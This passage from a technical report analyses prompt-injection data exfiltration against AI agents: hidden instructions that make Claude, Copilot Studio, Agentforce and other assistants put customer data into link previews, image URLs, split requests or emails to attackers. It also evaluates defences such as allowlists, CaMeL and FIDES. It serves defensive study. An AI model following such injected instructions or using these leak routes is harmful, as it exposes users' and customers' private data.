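A program could also try to send data out by using the session's valid token to ask Anthropic's server to fetch an outside address. Anthropic says the proxy blocks the request headers (settings sent along with a request) that would enable such a fetch. The web fetch rule would be a weak defence against this, because a program that calls the API writes the user message itself. It could put an address containing stolen data in that message, and the address would count as the user's.

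The fix covers only Anthropic's own domain. The default list in claude.ai also included GitHub and npm, and Rehberger warned that other entries might allow similar attacks. An account check would be harder to apply to those sites because Anthropic doesn't issue their accounts. But installing a package usually requires only a download and no login, so a proxy could block uploads and any request that carries a credential.

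Cowork's network controls also don't cover everything Claude does. According to the Cloud Security Alliance's *Top 6 Claude Cowork Security Risks to Watch*, web search and web fetch bypass them, and Claude's browser tool runs outside the virtual machine, in the user's own Chrome with the user's logins. Shortening the domain list therefore restricts the programs Claude runs but not the pages it opens. The Alliance recommends switching off web search unless employees need it.

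Claude Code has a stricter default for the programs it runs. It originally asked users to approve each network request, but Anthropic found that they approved about 93% of all permission requests. Anthropic then added a sandbox that blocks network access by default and lets Claude work inside it largely without asking, which reduced permission requests by 84%.

### Claudy Day and what remains open

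In March 2026, the upload route appeared in claude.ai again. *Claudy Day* (Luz, 2026) describes an attack by the security company Oasis Security that combined this route with two other flaws and worked in an ordinary chat with no connected apps.

The attack began with a Google advertisement that displayed a real `claude.com` address. Google checked only the domain, and `claude.com` had an open redirect, a page that forwards visitors to any address included in the link. A victim who clicked on what looked like an advertisement for Claude arrived at a new chat with a question already filled in. The link also contained further instructions in HTML tags, which the text box didn't show but Claude received when the victim pressed Enter.

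Those instructions made Claude search the victim's past conversations for sensitive information, write it to a file and upload the file with the attacker's key. An attacker could have used Google's targeting tools to show the advertisement only to particular people, including those on a list of email addresses.

The hidden text arrived as part of the user's own message, so a provenance rule that trusts user messages would accept any address in it, even though the user never saw the text. To prevent this, the software would have to show the user the complete message before sending it, or treat text from a link as untrusted.

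Anthropic had fixed the hidden-text flaw by the time Oasis published. Oasis described the upload route and the redirect as still "being addressed", and kept that wording in its last page update, on May 27, 2026. Anthropic's account of the proxy, published at about the same time, describes it as a repair to Cowork and doesn't mention claude.ai's container.

A company that uses code execution in claude.ai should therefore not assume that the Cowork repair protects it. It can test the route with two of its own accounts by asking Claude in one to upload a harmless file with the other's key. A refusal by Claude would prove little, since Rehberger got past such refusals, so the test has to show that the network control rejects the upload when Claude attempts it. If the file arrives, the company can turn off the container's network access, though Claude will then be unable to do some tasks that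 need new software packages.

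## Link previews and log viewers: other software that loads the link

The mail-order company might want its support assistant to answer in the team's channel on Slack, a workplace messaging app, as well as in the browser panel. If the company relies on the panel's CSP to block outside images, it loses that protection in Slack, because the CSP applies only to the panel's page and Slack has its own rules for displaying messages. The protection is also lost when a developer opens the conversation in a log viewer, a screen for reviewing what a model wrote.

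### How a preview replaces the click

When someone posts a link in a messaging app, the app often shows the page's title and a small picture under the message. Slack calls this unfurling. To get the title and picture, Slack's server requests the page, and the request contains the whole address, including any customer data that an injected instruction made the model put in the link.

A link in the browser panel leaks data only if the employee clicks it, but Slack requests the link as soon as the assistant posts it, which makes the attack zero-click even without an image. Even if the employee notices an odd address in the message, Slack has already sent the request. The request comes from Slack's server, so neither the employee's browser nor the company's firewall can block it. ReLeak's document attack on Copilot relied on similar behaviour by Microsoft's servers, which opened a link in a saved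 file.

Rehberger explained the risk in *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks*, published on Embrace The Red in August 2024. He had a short program post a link to his own site in Slack, and his server's log recorded a visit from Slack's preview software.

### PromptArmor's public test

In February 2026, PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* invited readers to test their own agents. When an agent posted a link to PromptArmor's test site, the site recorded which preview software visited and what data the address contained. Readers could then claim the log entry and report which agent and messaging app had produced it. They could also report combinations that produced no preview.

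OpenClaw, an AI agent that people often control through messaging apps, leaked data through Telegram with its default settings. Apostol's *AI Agents Leak Data via Messaging App Link Previews* also names Microsoft Teams with Copilot Studio, and Slack with certain bots. Copilot Studio has a setting that blocks links and images in an agent's answers, but a company that uses the agent in Teams should test whether the setting works there.

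The test, which has ended, showed that several widely used combinations leak. It didn't measure how common the problem is, because participants volunteered and reported their own results. A report that a combination is safe is weaker evidence than a report of a leak, because the participant may have turned previews off.

### A leak from a private channel

A company might try to contain the risk by letting the assistant post in only one private channel. Posting there without approval may seem safe because outsiders can't read the channel.

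Rehberger tested this with a Slack connector that Anthropic had published as an example of the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard for connecting AI assistants to other software. Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* describes a user asking Claude to summarize a document for the team. An instruction injected into the document led Claude to read the latest message in another channel, put it in a web address and post the link in the private channel. Slack's server then requested the link from Rehberger's site. If the link led to an image, Slack requested it several times.

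Anthropic's Slack connector left link previews on. Rehberger reported the flaw on May 27, 2025, and Anthropic archived the connector two days later, though he couldn't tell whether his report was the reason. Anthropic did not plan to fix the flaw, although people were still downloading the connector more than 14,000 times a week. VulnCheck's *Anthropic Slack MCP Server Data Exfiltration via Link Unfurling* gives the flaw, CVE-2025-34072, a critical severity score of 9.3, while Rehberger gave it 7.5. Anyone still using the archived version has to add the two missing settings or switch to a maintained connector.

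### Turning previews off

The two settings are `unfurl_links`, for pages that are mostly text, and `unfurl_media`, for images, video and audio. A program that posts to Slack can set both to `false` on each message so that Slack doesn't request the link.

Turning off only one of Slack's link preview settings is risky. Slack's *Unfurling links in messages* explains that Slack's servers have to fetch every address in a message to find out what kind of content it links to. With only one setting off, Slack would presumably still have to fetch the page to determine which setting applies. For the same reason, a message that shows no preview may already have leaked data. One of Slack's examples, a link to a text page, shows no preview by default. A developer should therefore test with a link to a server they control and check its log for a visit.

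Slack recommends that developers consider turning off previews for messages written by a language model. The preview settings apply to one message at a time, so every part of a program that posts the model's text has to include them.

Telegram also lets programs disable the preview for a message. OpenClaw users can turn previews off for all of the agent's Telegram messages by setting `linkPreview: false`, and PromptArmor reports that its test site stopped receiving data after this change. But OpenClaw's *Telegram* documentation still listed previews as on by default in August 2026, six months after the test.

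PromptArmor would like messaging companies to offer a link preview setting for a whole chat or channel, which would also cover messages from people. Slack previews links that employees post, so an employee who copies the assistant's answer into another channel can cause the leak even if previews are turned off for the assistant's own messages.

The company can also remove unapproved links before the answer leaves its own software. This works in any messaging app and protects employees who copy the answer or click its links. It also helps with email, where a program may load images when someone opens a message. *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* (Willison, 2026) discusses an agent with which this happened.

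### An image blocked in the app and loaded in the log

Removing a link from the displayed answer doesn't remove it from every copy. When a company builds an assistant on OpenAI's API, OpenAI can keep a log of the model's original answers for the company's developers to review. PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs* describes how an image that an app had blocked could still leak data from this log.

PromptArmor built a mock app for checking the identity of bank customers. Its assistant drew on six sources, one of which contained web text with an injected instruction. The assistant's answer included an image whose address contained the customer's personal and financial details. A second model that checked the answers flagged this one as malicious, and the app didn't display it.

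A developer investigating the flagged conversation would probably open it in OpenAI's log viewer. The viewer formatted answers as Markdown, so the developer's browser loaded the image and sent the attacker the customer's details, including passport and driving licence information and net worth.

The app's check worked, but it also gave the developer a reason to open the dangerous answer. A CSP in the app, or software that strips images from the displayed text, would not protect the developer's log viewer either. PromptArmor gives the example of an answer from the AI search engine Perplexity that was blank after software removed an image. A user might give such an answer a thumbs-down, which could lead a developer to review it. PromptArmor did not show this happening at Perplexity.

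This attack is less certain to work than one in the chat itself, because someone has to open that particular conversation. But developers are more likely to open suspicious conversations than ordinary ones, and an attacker can wait for that to happen.

PromptArmor found the same flaw in the preview screens where developers test chats, assistants and agents on OpenAI's platform. The starter app for ChatKit, OpenAI's kit for building chat products, also displayed images insecurely. Developers base their own products on the starter app, so those products could have the same problem.

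PromptArmor reported the flaw in the log viewer on November 17, 2025, through Bugcrowd, a company that screens security reports for OpenAI. After four follow-up messages, Bugcrowd closed the report on December 4 as not applicable, before OpenAI had seen it. After PromptArmor published the flaw, OpenAI confirmed it, reopened the report on January 22, 2026, and said it was working on a fix.

PromptArmor's timeline ends there. A developer can test the current log viewer by having a model output an image URL that points to the developer's own server, then opening the log entry and checking whether the server receives a request. If it does, reviewing flagged answers as plain text is safer.

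### Silent Egress: an instruction in the page description

Previews can also expose a model to injected instructions. Some agents automatically fetch a linked page and add its title, description and text to the model's input. The description is in the page's code and normally isn't displayed, so a person reading the page wouldn't notice an instruction there. Lan and colleagues call this implicit prompt injection, and in an experiment at eBay they measured how often it made an agent send out a secret.

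Everything ran locally. One server created the malicious pages, and another recorded every request that reached the attacker's address. The only model was Qwen2.5 7B.

They varied three things:

- **Location.** The instruction was in the page's title, description, main text or link text.
- **Delivery.** The agent opened the page directly or through redirects.
- **Method.** The instruction asked for the secret in one request or split into four pieces.

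Each of the 16 combinations was run 30 times, and at least one request reached the attacker in 423 of the 480 runs (88.1%). The paper's headline figure of about 89% is the rate for redirected pages. The rate for pages opened directly was 88%, so redirects made almost no difference.

The location of the injected instruction also mattered little when the model sent the secret in one request. The attack succeeded in every run with it in the title, main text or link text, and in 96.7% of runs with it in the description. In 120 further runs with harmless pages, the agent never contacted the attacker's server, which is good evidence that the injected text caused the requests.

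In the Slack and log viewer attacks, the dangerous address was part of the model's answer, where software could find it. In 95% of the successful attacks in this experiment, the address was only in a tool call.

### Splitting a secret over several requests

Software that scans each request separately can miss a secret sent in pieces. For example, an injected instruction could make the support assistant send a ten-digit phone number as two groups of three digits and two groups of two. A DLP filter looking for phone numbers would find none, and the attacker could then join the groups. In the experiment, the model numbered the pieces so the attacker could put them in order.

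Lan and colleagues found that the first request contained sensitive information in 96.7% of runs when the model was told to send the whole secret, and in 26.3% when it was told to split the secret.

Part of this fall came from attacks that failed completely. Qwen followed the longer instructions less reliably, and at least one request got out in about 77% of the runs with splitting, compared with 99% of the runs without it. Among the runs in which a request got out, the first request contained sensitive information in about 34% with splitting and 97% without, a relative fall of 65%.

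The measurement also has a problem. The paper's definition of sensitive information includes any fragment of the secret, so the first piece of a split secret should count. Checking the first three requests instead of only the first should find at least as many leaks, but the reported figure for split secrets falls from 26.3% to 15.8%. The researchers' software must have counted something narrower than the definition.

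The 73% therefore doesn't measure how many leaks a real filter would miss. The researchers ran their filters only on secrets sent in one request and didn't test whether splitting a secret across several requests gets past them. Splitting could plausibly work, since a filter can't detect a phone number from two of its digits.

Software would have to examine all of a session's requests together to detect a split secret. Lan and colleagues suggest doing this and limiting the number of requests per session. A domain allowlist doesn't depend on detecting the secret, because it blocks any request to an unapproved domain, whatever the request contains.

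### What the comparison of defences tested

To compare the defences, the researchers ran each one 30 times against one of the most successful attacks. The agent opened a page directly, and the page's main text contained an instruction to send the secret in one request.

| Defence | Runs in which the model tried to send the secret | Runs in which a request got out |
|---|---|---|
| None | 30 | 30 |
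| Rule in the prompt | 20 | 20 |
| Tags around web content | 30 | 30 |
| Rule and tags | 17 | 17 |
| Domain allowlist | 30 | 0 |
| "Redirect detection" | 25 | 0 |
| Keyword filter | 7 | 0 |
| Entropy filter | 0 | 0 |
| All of these together | 0 | 0 |

Adding tags to the rule in the prompt may have made no further difference, since the gap between 20 and 17 runs could easily be due to chance.

The software's "redirect detection" blocked numeric internet addresses, certain domain endings such as `.xyz`, and paths containing words such as "steal" or "collect". The name is misleading because the software didn't follow redirects, and this part of the experiment had none. The attacker's domain, `evil-collector.net`, wasn't a numeric address and didn't have a banned ending, so a word in the path must have triggered the block, which an attacker could avoid by choosing another word.

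A real redirect check would stop at each redirect, read the next address and compare it with the allowlist before continuing. Lan and colleagues recommend combining an allowlist with such checks, but they did not test the combination.

The entropy filter was meant to catch values that resemble random passwords or keys. It blocked any value longer than ten characters with a Shannon entropy, a measure of how varied the characters are, above 4.0 bits per character. A value made only of digits can't exceed log₂ 10, or about 3.3 bits, so the filter would never block a phone number or an order number. It would also miss the sample key in the paper, `SECRET_API_KEY_12345`, which has an entropy of about 3.85.

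The model never tried to send anything while the entropy filter was on, so the filter had nothing to block. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids random-looking values when such a filter is active, but they do not explain how it would get information about the filter.

They also propose taint tracking, which labels everything from a web page as untrusted and carries the label over to any tool call the page influenced. The software could then block a suspicious request even if it contained only two digits. It is hard to tell what influenced a call, though, because the model processes all its input together. If the software labels every call made after the agent has read a web page, the agent can no longer open a second page without approval. The researchers did not test this proposal either.

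### What a local test can show about commercial products

The 88.1% success rate is not an estimate for ChatGPT, Claude or Copilot. Lan and colleagues describe their setup as favourable to the attacker, because the secret was already in the model's input and the standing instructions covered only the tool format. They also call their success rates a lower bound, because they used simple attack text. The setup raises the measured rate and the simple text lowers it, but a test of one small model can't show which effect would be larger in a commercial product.

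The researchers did not test commercial products, partly to avoid breaking the companies' terms of service. They argue that stronger models might be more vulnerable because they follow instructions and use tools more reliably. Later results for leading models suggest the opposite, at least for simple injections.

The findings about where to put a check are more likely to apply to other models. A check of the visible answer can't find data that is only in a tool call, whichever model made the call. An allowlist on the web tool works the same way for a weak model as for a strong one.

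However, the experiment had only one route for data to leave, which the allowlist covered, and a commercial assistant usually has others. The mail-order company could put the same allowlist on its assistant's web tool and block every unapproved request there. But if the assistant also posts in Slack with link previews on, Slack's server will still request the attacker's link.

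## Customer service agents that send email: restricting the recipients

An agent that can send email can leak data without a link or an image, by writing a customer's record into a message and sending it to the attacker. A list of permitted domains does little to prevent this, because customers use Gmail, Outlook and many other mail providers, and an attacker can open an account with any of them. The company has to decide who may receive a message, and sometimes what each recipient may read.

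### Zenity's replica of a McKinsey agent

In early 2025, the security company Zenity attacked a replica of a customer service agent that the consulting firm McKinsey had built with Microsoft's Copilot Studio. McKinsey's agent read emailed requests, looked up missing details in customer databases and forwarded each request to the right employee. Zenity's replica could read a file about customer accounts and a Salesforce CRM.

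Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer* describes an attack in three stages:

1. The researchers wrote to the agent and got it to reply with the names of its files and tools.
2. They sent an email that named the customer file and asked for its contents. Seconds later, the agent emailed them the whole file.
3. They sent another email that named the tool for reading Salesforce records. The agent sent back dozens of complete records, as many as fitted into one message.

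The attack was zero-click. The file in the replica had only about ten rows, but Zenity says the agent can leak about 100 rows at a time, and an attacker could keep sending emails.

This was possible because any email to the inbox triggered the agent, and the agent could write to any address. Zenity advises companies to list the exact senders who can trigger an agent, which suits an internal help desk but not a public support address. Restricting the recipients would have been easier. Judging by Zenity's description, McKinsey's agent only had to forward requests to employees, so limiting its recipients to a fixed list of employees would have let it do its job and blocked every email to the attacker.

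Microsoft restricted neither setting. Zenity reported the flaw on February 21, 2025, and Microsoft rated it critical, fixed it on April 24 and paid an $8,000 reward. Zenity's tests suggest the fix was mainly a classifier that recognizes injected instructions. It stopped Zenity's original emails, but an attacker can word the request differently, as Office 365 for IT Pros' *Copilot Studio Agent Vulnerability to Prompt Injection* points out. Microsoft's injection classifier failed again in the ReLeak attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot in 2026.

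Office 365 for IT Pros also says administrators would probably not notice such a leak afterwards, because they would have to find one suspicious message among the records of everything the agent had done. Zenity found more than 3,000 Copilot Studio agents reachable from the internet, according to SecurityWeek's *Major Enterprise AI Assistants Can Be Abused for Data Theft, Manipulation*. Some of those agents may have had nothing worth stealing or no way to send email.

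### ShareLeak and PipeLeak: from a public form to an email

On April 15, 2026, Capsule Security published two attacks in which the injected instruction arrived through a web form. ShareLeak targeted agents built with Copilot Studio, and PipeLeak targeted Salesforce's Agentforce. Help Net Security's *Capsule Security debuts with $7 million funding to secure AI agent behavior* (2026) reports that Capsule launched a product for blocking unsafe agent actions at the same time, so it had a commercial reason to publicize the attacks.

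In ShareLeak, an attacker typed instructions into a SharePoint form that a Copilot Studio agent processed. Security Boulevard's *Microsoft and Salesforce Patch AI Agent Flaws That Could Leak Sensitive Data* (2026) explains that the instructions could trigger the agent's connected actions and send customer data to the attacker's email address. Capsule reported the flaw on November 24, 2025, and Microsoft patched it on January 15, 2026. STAR Labs' *Copilot Studio* (2026) lists it as CVE-2026-21520, with a CVSS score of 7.5, a critical rating from Microsoft and no known exploitation.

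In Capsule's tests, a safety check flagged the request as suspicious but the data still leaked, according to the news site Claw Times. A check that only raises a flag can't prevent a leak by email, because nobody can take back a sent message. The software that sends the email has to wait for the result and refuse to send if the check fails. Claw Times presents the leak as evidence that Microsoft's January patch failed, but the VentureBeat report it summarizes doesn't draw that conclusion.

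PipeLeak started with a public lead form, as ForcedLeak had the year before. The agent treated the text in the form as an instruction and emailed out data about the company's leads. Salesforce's Trusted URLs rule doesn't check recipients, so it didn't stop the email. When Capsule published its findings, Salesforce had not issued a CVE number or a public advisory.

CSO Online's *Copilot and Agentforce fall to form-based prompt injection tricks* (2026) reports that Salesforce called the problem "configuration-specific". This is partly true, because each company decides whether its agent can send email. But a public lead form and an agent that emails people are both ordinary things for a Salesforce customer to want, and an administrator could easily enable both without realizing that together they let a stranger request the company's data. Salesforce has since fixed the specific attack and made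 human confirmation the default when an agent sends email.

The new default didn't cover other ways of sending data out. Infosecurity Magazine's *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI Agent Risk* describes SalesBleed, in which Zenity again put instructions in a lead form but used DNS, the system that looks up domain names, to get the data past Trusted URLs. Salesforce fixed that flaw on August 18, 2026.

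### Copilot Cowork: a message to the user's own inbox

Microsoft's Copilot Cowork (not to be confused with Anthropic's Claude Cowork) carries out office tasks with the user's own permissions. Microsoft's documentation says that Copilot Cowork asks before sending an email or posting in Teams. In May 2026, PromptArmor reported that it sent messages without asking when the user was the only recipient, and that users had no setting to change this.

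The exception for messages to the user can still leak data to an attacker, even though the user already has access to that data. Outlook and Teams can load outside images when the user opens a message, so an attacker can receive data in an image's URL without being a recipient.

PromptArmor hid its instruction in a skill file, a set of directions the agent follows for a certain kind of task. The malicious part took up five of the file's 81 lines. When the user asked for a review of the week's work, the agent collected download links for the user's recent files and put them in image addresses in a Teams message. Anyone with such a link can download the file without logging in, so a short web address could leak an entire document. The agent's activity display never showed the content of the message.

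The attack worked in all five trials. The same instruction also worked when PromptArmor selected the stronger model Claude Opus 4.7, which searched more thoroughly and leaked more documents. The user in the demonstration had uploaded the skill file, but PromptArmor's *Securing Microsoft Copilot Cowork* lists emails as another source of injected instructions, since the agent can read them when it sorts the inbox. Users can also schedule a task such as a weekly review, which the agent then repeats with nobody watching.

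PromptArmor describes this as a risk in the product's design rather than a single bug, and mentions no fix by Microsoft. Administrators can block downloads of sensitive files, which makes the stolen links useless. But employees can then view those files only in a browser, and can't print them or open them in Word or Excel.

As a narrower remedy, Microsoft could remove outside images from every message the agent writes, including messages to the user. Asking for approval would be less reliable, because an employee who saw only the visible text would probably approve an ordinary summary of the week, and if the approval dialog displayed the image, loading it could send the request.

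### What each recipient rule breaks and misses

The mail-order company might want an agent to answer customers' emails without an employee present. It could restrict the recipients in four ways.

| Rule | What it breaks | What it misses |
|---|---|---|
| Fixed list of recipients | Replies to customers | Outside images in a permitted message |
| Company's own domain only | Replies to customers and suppliers | Outside images, and employees who shouldn't see the data |
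| Address on the customer's record only | Replies to new customers, or to a customer who writes from another address | Attackers who are customers, and records that an attacker has changed |
| Human approval | Replies when nobody is on duty | Harmful messages that an employee approves |

A fixed list of recipients is the strongest rule, and it suits any agent that only passes requests to staff. Allowing the whole company domain is more convenient, but it lets the agent send a salary list to any employee. Some mailboxes also forward everything to an outside address, and a group address on the company's domain can have outside members. Both rules need a ban on externally hosted images, as the Copilot Cowork case shows.

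A company might consider allowing an agent that answers the public to reply only to the sender. This rule would not have stopped Zenity's attack, because the attacker was the sender.

Sending only to the address on the customer's record is better, provided that code looks up the address and the model can't replace it. If a stranger pretends to be Ana Silva, the reply still goes to the real Ana. This protection fails if the agent can change the record. In another Zenity demonstration reported by SecurityWeek, malicious support cases could make Salesforce's Einstein assistant replace the email addresses on all the cases, so that messages to customers went through the attacker's server. Replies sent only to the address on record would still have reached the attacker. Salesforce fixed the flaw on July 11, 2025.

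The attacker can also become a customer by ordering something cheap. The agent is then allowed to email the attacker's address, and the attacker can inject an instruction to include Ana's phone number. Rules that only restrict recipients can't catch this, because the recipient is legitimate and the problem is in the content.

The company can prevent data exfiltration by restricting what the agent reads. Before the model starts, code identifies the customer from the sender's address and opens only that customer's records. The order lookup rejects order numbers that belong to other customers. An email containing injected instructions could then obtain only the sender's own data, and the reply would go to the address on the sender's record. This takes only ordinary programming, so it is a sensible first choice for a support desk. It doesn't work for tasks that involve several people's data,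 such as a complaint about a parcel that went to a neighbour.

### When to ask a person

Human approval can handle cases that a fixed rule can't, but it gives up much of the benefit of an automatic agent. AdExchanger's *How Agentic AI Can Break In The Real World* describes a test by Aaron Costello of the security company AppOmni on ServiceNow, a platform for support tickets and other business processes. Costello put an instruction in a ticket to email data from somebody else's ticket. The agent that read it could call on other agents to read records and send messages, so it didn't need to send the email itself.

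ServiceNow replied that the system was working "as designed". It updated its documentation and warned customers, but left cooperation between agents on by default. Costello says the only fix is to put a person in the loop, and acknowledges that this would undercut the automation. But a recipient rule in the email tool would also have stopped a message to an outsider, whichever agent requested it.

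People also approve harmful actions, as Hossain and colleagues found, so it would be better to have code approve routine replies and leave only the unusual ones to a person. To decide whether a reply is routine, the code has to check where its contents came from and who is allowed to read them. Two research designs from 2025, CaMeL and FIDES, track both.

### CaMeL: fixing the plan before reading the email

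CaMeL comes from *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025) by Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues. It builds on Willison's 2023 Dual LLM pattern, which divides the work between two language models. The privileged model receives the user's request and decides which tools to use, but never reads untrusted text. The quarantined model reads the untrusted text but has no tools.

In CaMeL, the privileged model writes the plan as a short Python program before the system reads any email. Ordinary software, called the interpreter, runs the program and calls the tools. When a step involves reading an email, the interpreter passes the text to the quarantined model and stores the answer as a variable, a named value that later steps can use without the privileged model seeing it. An injected instruction can change that value but can't add a step to the program.

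Separating the models is not enough. Suppose the plan is to send a document to the address given in an email. Injected text can make the quarantined model return the attacker's address, and the interpreter would carry out the original plan with the wrong recipient.

CaMeL therefore tracks provenance by attaching a label to every value. *CaMeLoT* (2026), a later extension of the design, explains that the label records the value's sources and the people who may read it. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a small Python function that takes the requested action with its labelled values and returns allow or deny.

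### One email, step by step

A customer named Mallory writes to the mail-order company about a late parcel and gives order number 5512, which belongs to Ana Silva. In a hidden paragraph, Mallory also asks for Ana's phone number. An employee who hasn't noticed any of this asks the assistant to answer the latest message with the status of the order it mentions.

The privileged model receives only the employee's request and writes this plan:

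1. Fetch the latest message.
2. Have the quarantined model find the order number in it.
3. Look up that order.
4. Have the quarantined model draft a reply from the message and the order.
5. Send the draft to the person who wrote the message.

The interpreter carries out the first four steps. The quarantined model reads the hidden paragraph and may obey it by writing Ana's phone number into the draft. The labels then look like this:

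| Value | Source | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| Message | Mallory | Support desk, Mallory |
| Order 5512, as stored | Order system | Support desk, Ana |
| Draft reply | Both of these | Support desk |

The draft contains information from the message and the order, so only someone allowed to read both may read it. The support desk is the only reader listed in both rows. In step 5, the policy blocks the email because the recipient, Mallory, isn't a permitted reader.

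If Ana had asked about her own order, she would have been allowed to read both the message and the order, so the software would have sent her the reply without asking anyone for approval.

The draft keeps the same label even if the quarantined model encodes the phone number in base64 or spells it out in the first letters of each sentence, because the label depends on the text's source, Ana's record, and not on its wording. A DLP filter would have to recognize the phone number in the text. The labels can't stop the model from writing a false or useless reply to a permitted recipient.

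### FIDES: two conditions for sending

*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes FIDES, a similar system that Microsoft's researchers developed. Information-flow control means attaching labels to data and checking them wherever the data might leave. Each label in FIDES has two parts.

The first part is integrity, which is either trusted or untrusted. A value derived from several others is trusted only if all of them are. The second is confidentiality, which can be a set of permitted readers. If *A* is the set of people who may read one document and *B* the set who may read another, only the people in both sets, *A* ∩ *B*, may read a text based on both documents. An email with recipients *R* and content readable by *S* passes the confidentiality check if *R* ⊆ *S*, meaning that every recipient is a permitted reader.

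The planning model in FIDES chooses one step at a time instead of writing the whole plan in advance. The software replaces untrusted results with variables before the model can read them. If the model needs to read a result, it can open the variable, but from then on the software treats the model's decisions as untrusted and may block actions such as sending email.

The planning model can also restrict the quarantined model to a few possible answers. For the support desk, these might be "order status", "return", "complaint", "address change" and "other". A choice among five answers carries at most log₂ 5 (about 2.3) bits, far too little for an injected instruction. The attacker can still influence which of the five procedures the agent follows, so the company should not let the quarantined model's answer trigger a refund.

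FIDES has two basic policies for sending data:

- **Trusted action.** The decision to send, and the choice of recipient if the policy requires it, must not depend on untrusted text.
- **Permitted flow.** Every recipient must be allowed to read the content.

Costa and colleagues explain that the two policies can be used separately or together. If the software requires only a trusted action, it treats any disclosure that the user's request led to as intentional. In the example, the employee's request led to the reply, and Mallory's address could also count as trusted because mail servers can verify a sender's domain. The policy would then let the assistant send Ana's details to Mallory, although the employee never intended to disclose them.

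A later Microsoft sample policy for posting in Teams has the same property because it accepts either condition. That may suit an employee who knowingly shares a document with a colleague, but a support desk should require that every recipient of an outgoing email be allowed to read its contents, whoever made the request.

### Benchmark results and their cost

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES on AgentDojo, a set of simulated office, travel, banking and Slack tasks with prompt injections. They used GPT-4o to plan and to read untrusted text. The table gives the number of successful attacks after the researchers removed misjudged cases, and the share of tasks completed when there was no attack. The percentages are simple averages across the four environments.

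| Agent | Successful attacks | Tasks completed without attacks |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent | 152 | 84% |
| Ordinary agent with policy checks | 0 | 42% |
| FIDES without policy checks | 21 | 61% |
| FIDES with policy checks | 0 | 50% |

The policy checks reduced successful attacks to zero. Hiding text in variables alone reduced them from 152 to 21, but the planning model could still open a variable and follow instructions inside it. Hiding text mainly helps the agent do more work under the checks, because untrusted text affects fewer of its decisions.

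The zeros result partly from the test's design. The researchers labelled a type of data as untrusted if at least one attack in the benchmark used it, so they knew in advance where every attack would come from. A company doesn't have that information, and if it labels the body of an email as untrusted but forgets the names of attachments, an instruction in a file name gets past the policy.

The drop in completed tasks is large, partly because GPT-4o confused variable names or read untrusted text when it didn't have to. OpenAI's o1, a model trained to reason before answering, completed 68% of the travel tasks, compared with 41% for GPT-4o. Both models are old, and a current one would probably fail fewer tasks through such mistakes.

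A better model can't recover the other losses, because the policies are supposed to block those tasks. In many of the banking tasks, for example, the user asks the agent to read a file and follow the instructions in it. FIDES treats the file as untrusted, so it refuses to schedule a payment. Customer service has the same difficulty, because a customer's email is untrusted but also contains the request the agent is supposed to carry out. Under these rules, an agent can answer a question about an order, but it would have to ask somebody before acting on most other requests.

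A later paper by some of the same Microsoft researchers gives one figure for both CaMeL and FIDES, a reduction of up to 30% in completed AgentDojo tasks. Both designs also have the model generate more text, which makes each task more expensive.

### Objections to tracking labels

Labels follow data from one value to another, but information can also leak through the agent's decisions. Suppose a program sends Mallory the fixed sentence "We will reply soon" only if Ana has an open order. The sentence contains nothing from Ana's record, so Mallory is allowed to read it, but Mallory can infer from receiving it that Ana has an open order. Costa and colleagues acknowledge that FIDES doesn't prevent this kind of leak, called an implicit flow. Preventing it completely would require blocking almost every visible action after the agent had read something confidential, which they consider too restrictive.

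Garby (2026), in *The LLMbda Calculus*, raises a related problem with CaMeL. A program might set an answer to "no" and change it to "yes" if a confidential condition is true. If the condition is true, the software can label the new answer as confidential. If it is false, that change never runs, so the "no" keeps its original label even though it reveals that the condition was false. CaMeL misses a label for this reason in one of Garby's examples.

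Garby also argues that software with such gaps is hard to audit, and that building the two-model design into CaMeL and FIDES makes them rigid. Neither system gives a complete guarantee for the varied programs agents write. These objections are correct, but they matter less for a support desk than the attacks the labels stop. An implicit flow usually reveals one yes-or-no answer at a time, whereas Zenity's agent sent dozens of full records in one email.

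Another difficulty arises when several agents work together. *Can CaMeLs Talk?* (2026) extends CaMeL to such systems and describes an instruction, injected into a database, that passes from one agent to another. ServiceNow's agents had this weakness. The label recording where text came from has to stay attached when one agent passes the text to another, or the second agent will treat the injected instruction as a request from the first.

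### PRUDENTIA: fewer requests for approval

*Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues, 2026) argues that evaluations have compared protected and ordinary agents unfairly. They usually count a blocked action as a failure but let the ordinary agent act freely. In practice, a company worried about prompt injection would have the ordinary agent ask a person before every important action, so the researchers counted how many approvals each agent needed.

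PRUDENTIA is an agent built on top of FIDES. Its planning model receives each value's label and each tool's policy, so it can look for a plan that the policies allow. It can also prompt the user to endorse an untrusted text, which the software then treats as trusted. If an email lists ten tasks, the user endorses the email once instead of approving ten actions.

The results on AgentDojo with OpenAI's o3-mini were:

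| Agent | Approvals needed in total | Tasks completed with no approval |
|---|---|---|
| Ordinary agent that asks before every important action | 48.2 | 24.3% |
| Ordinary agent with policy checks | 32.4 | 35.5% |
| FIDES | 18.8 | 50.1% |
| PRUDENTIA | about 17 | 59.1% |

The totals are averaged over five runs and cover only tasks the agent completed. With another model, o4-mini, PRUDENTIA needed 19.2 approvals and FIDES needed 36.8. PRUDENTIA also completed slightly fewer tasks, 73.2% compared with 75.7%. The reduction in approvals therefore depends a good deal on the model.

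On a second benchmark, WASP, PRUDENTIA needed no approvals and blocked every attack, while injected text diverted the ordinary agent in 14.6% to 61.1% of cases. But the user tasks in WASP were only to post a comment or vote for a post, which the agent could do without reading the untrusted text. A support agent has to read nearly every email it answers.

Kolluri and colleagues assume that a person always approves the right actions and stops the harmful ones. Endorsement makes this assumption more important, because one mistaken endorsement lets the agent act on everything in the text. An employee might endorse Mallory's complaint after reading only the visible part. A support desk would be safer if employees approved individual actions, or endorsed a short extract, such as an order number, instead of the whole email.

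The researchers didn't add a similar way to approve the release of confidential data in general. They thought that decision depended too much on the situation, so PRUDENTIA requests approval for each message. Labels could supply the facts for those requests, for example that a draft contains Ana's record and Mallory isn't allowed to read it.

### What Microsoft has released

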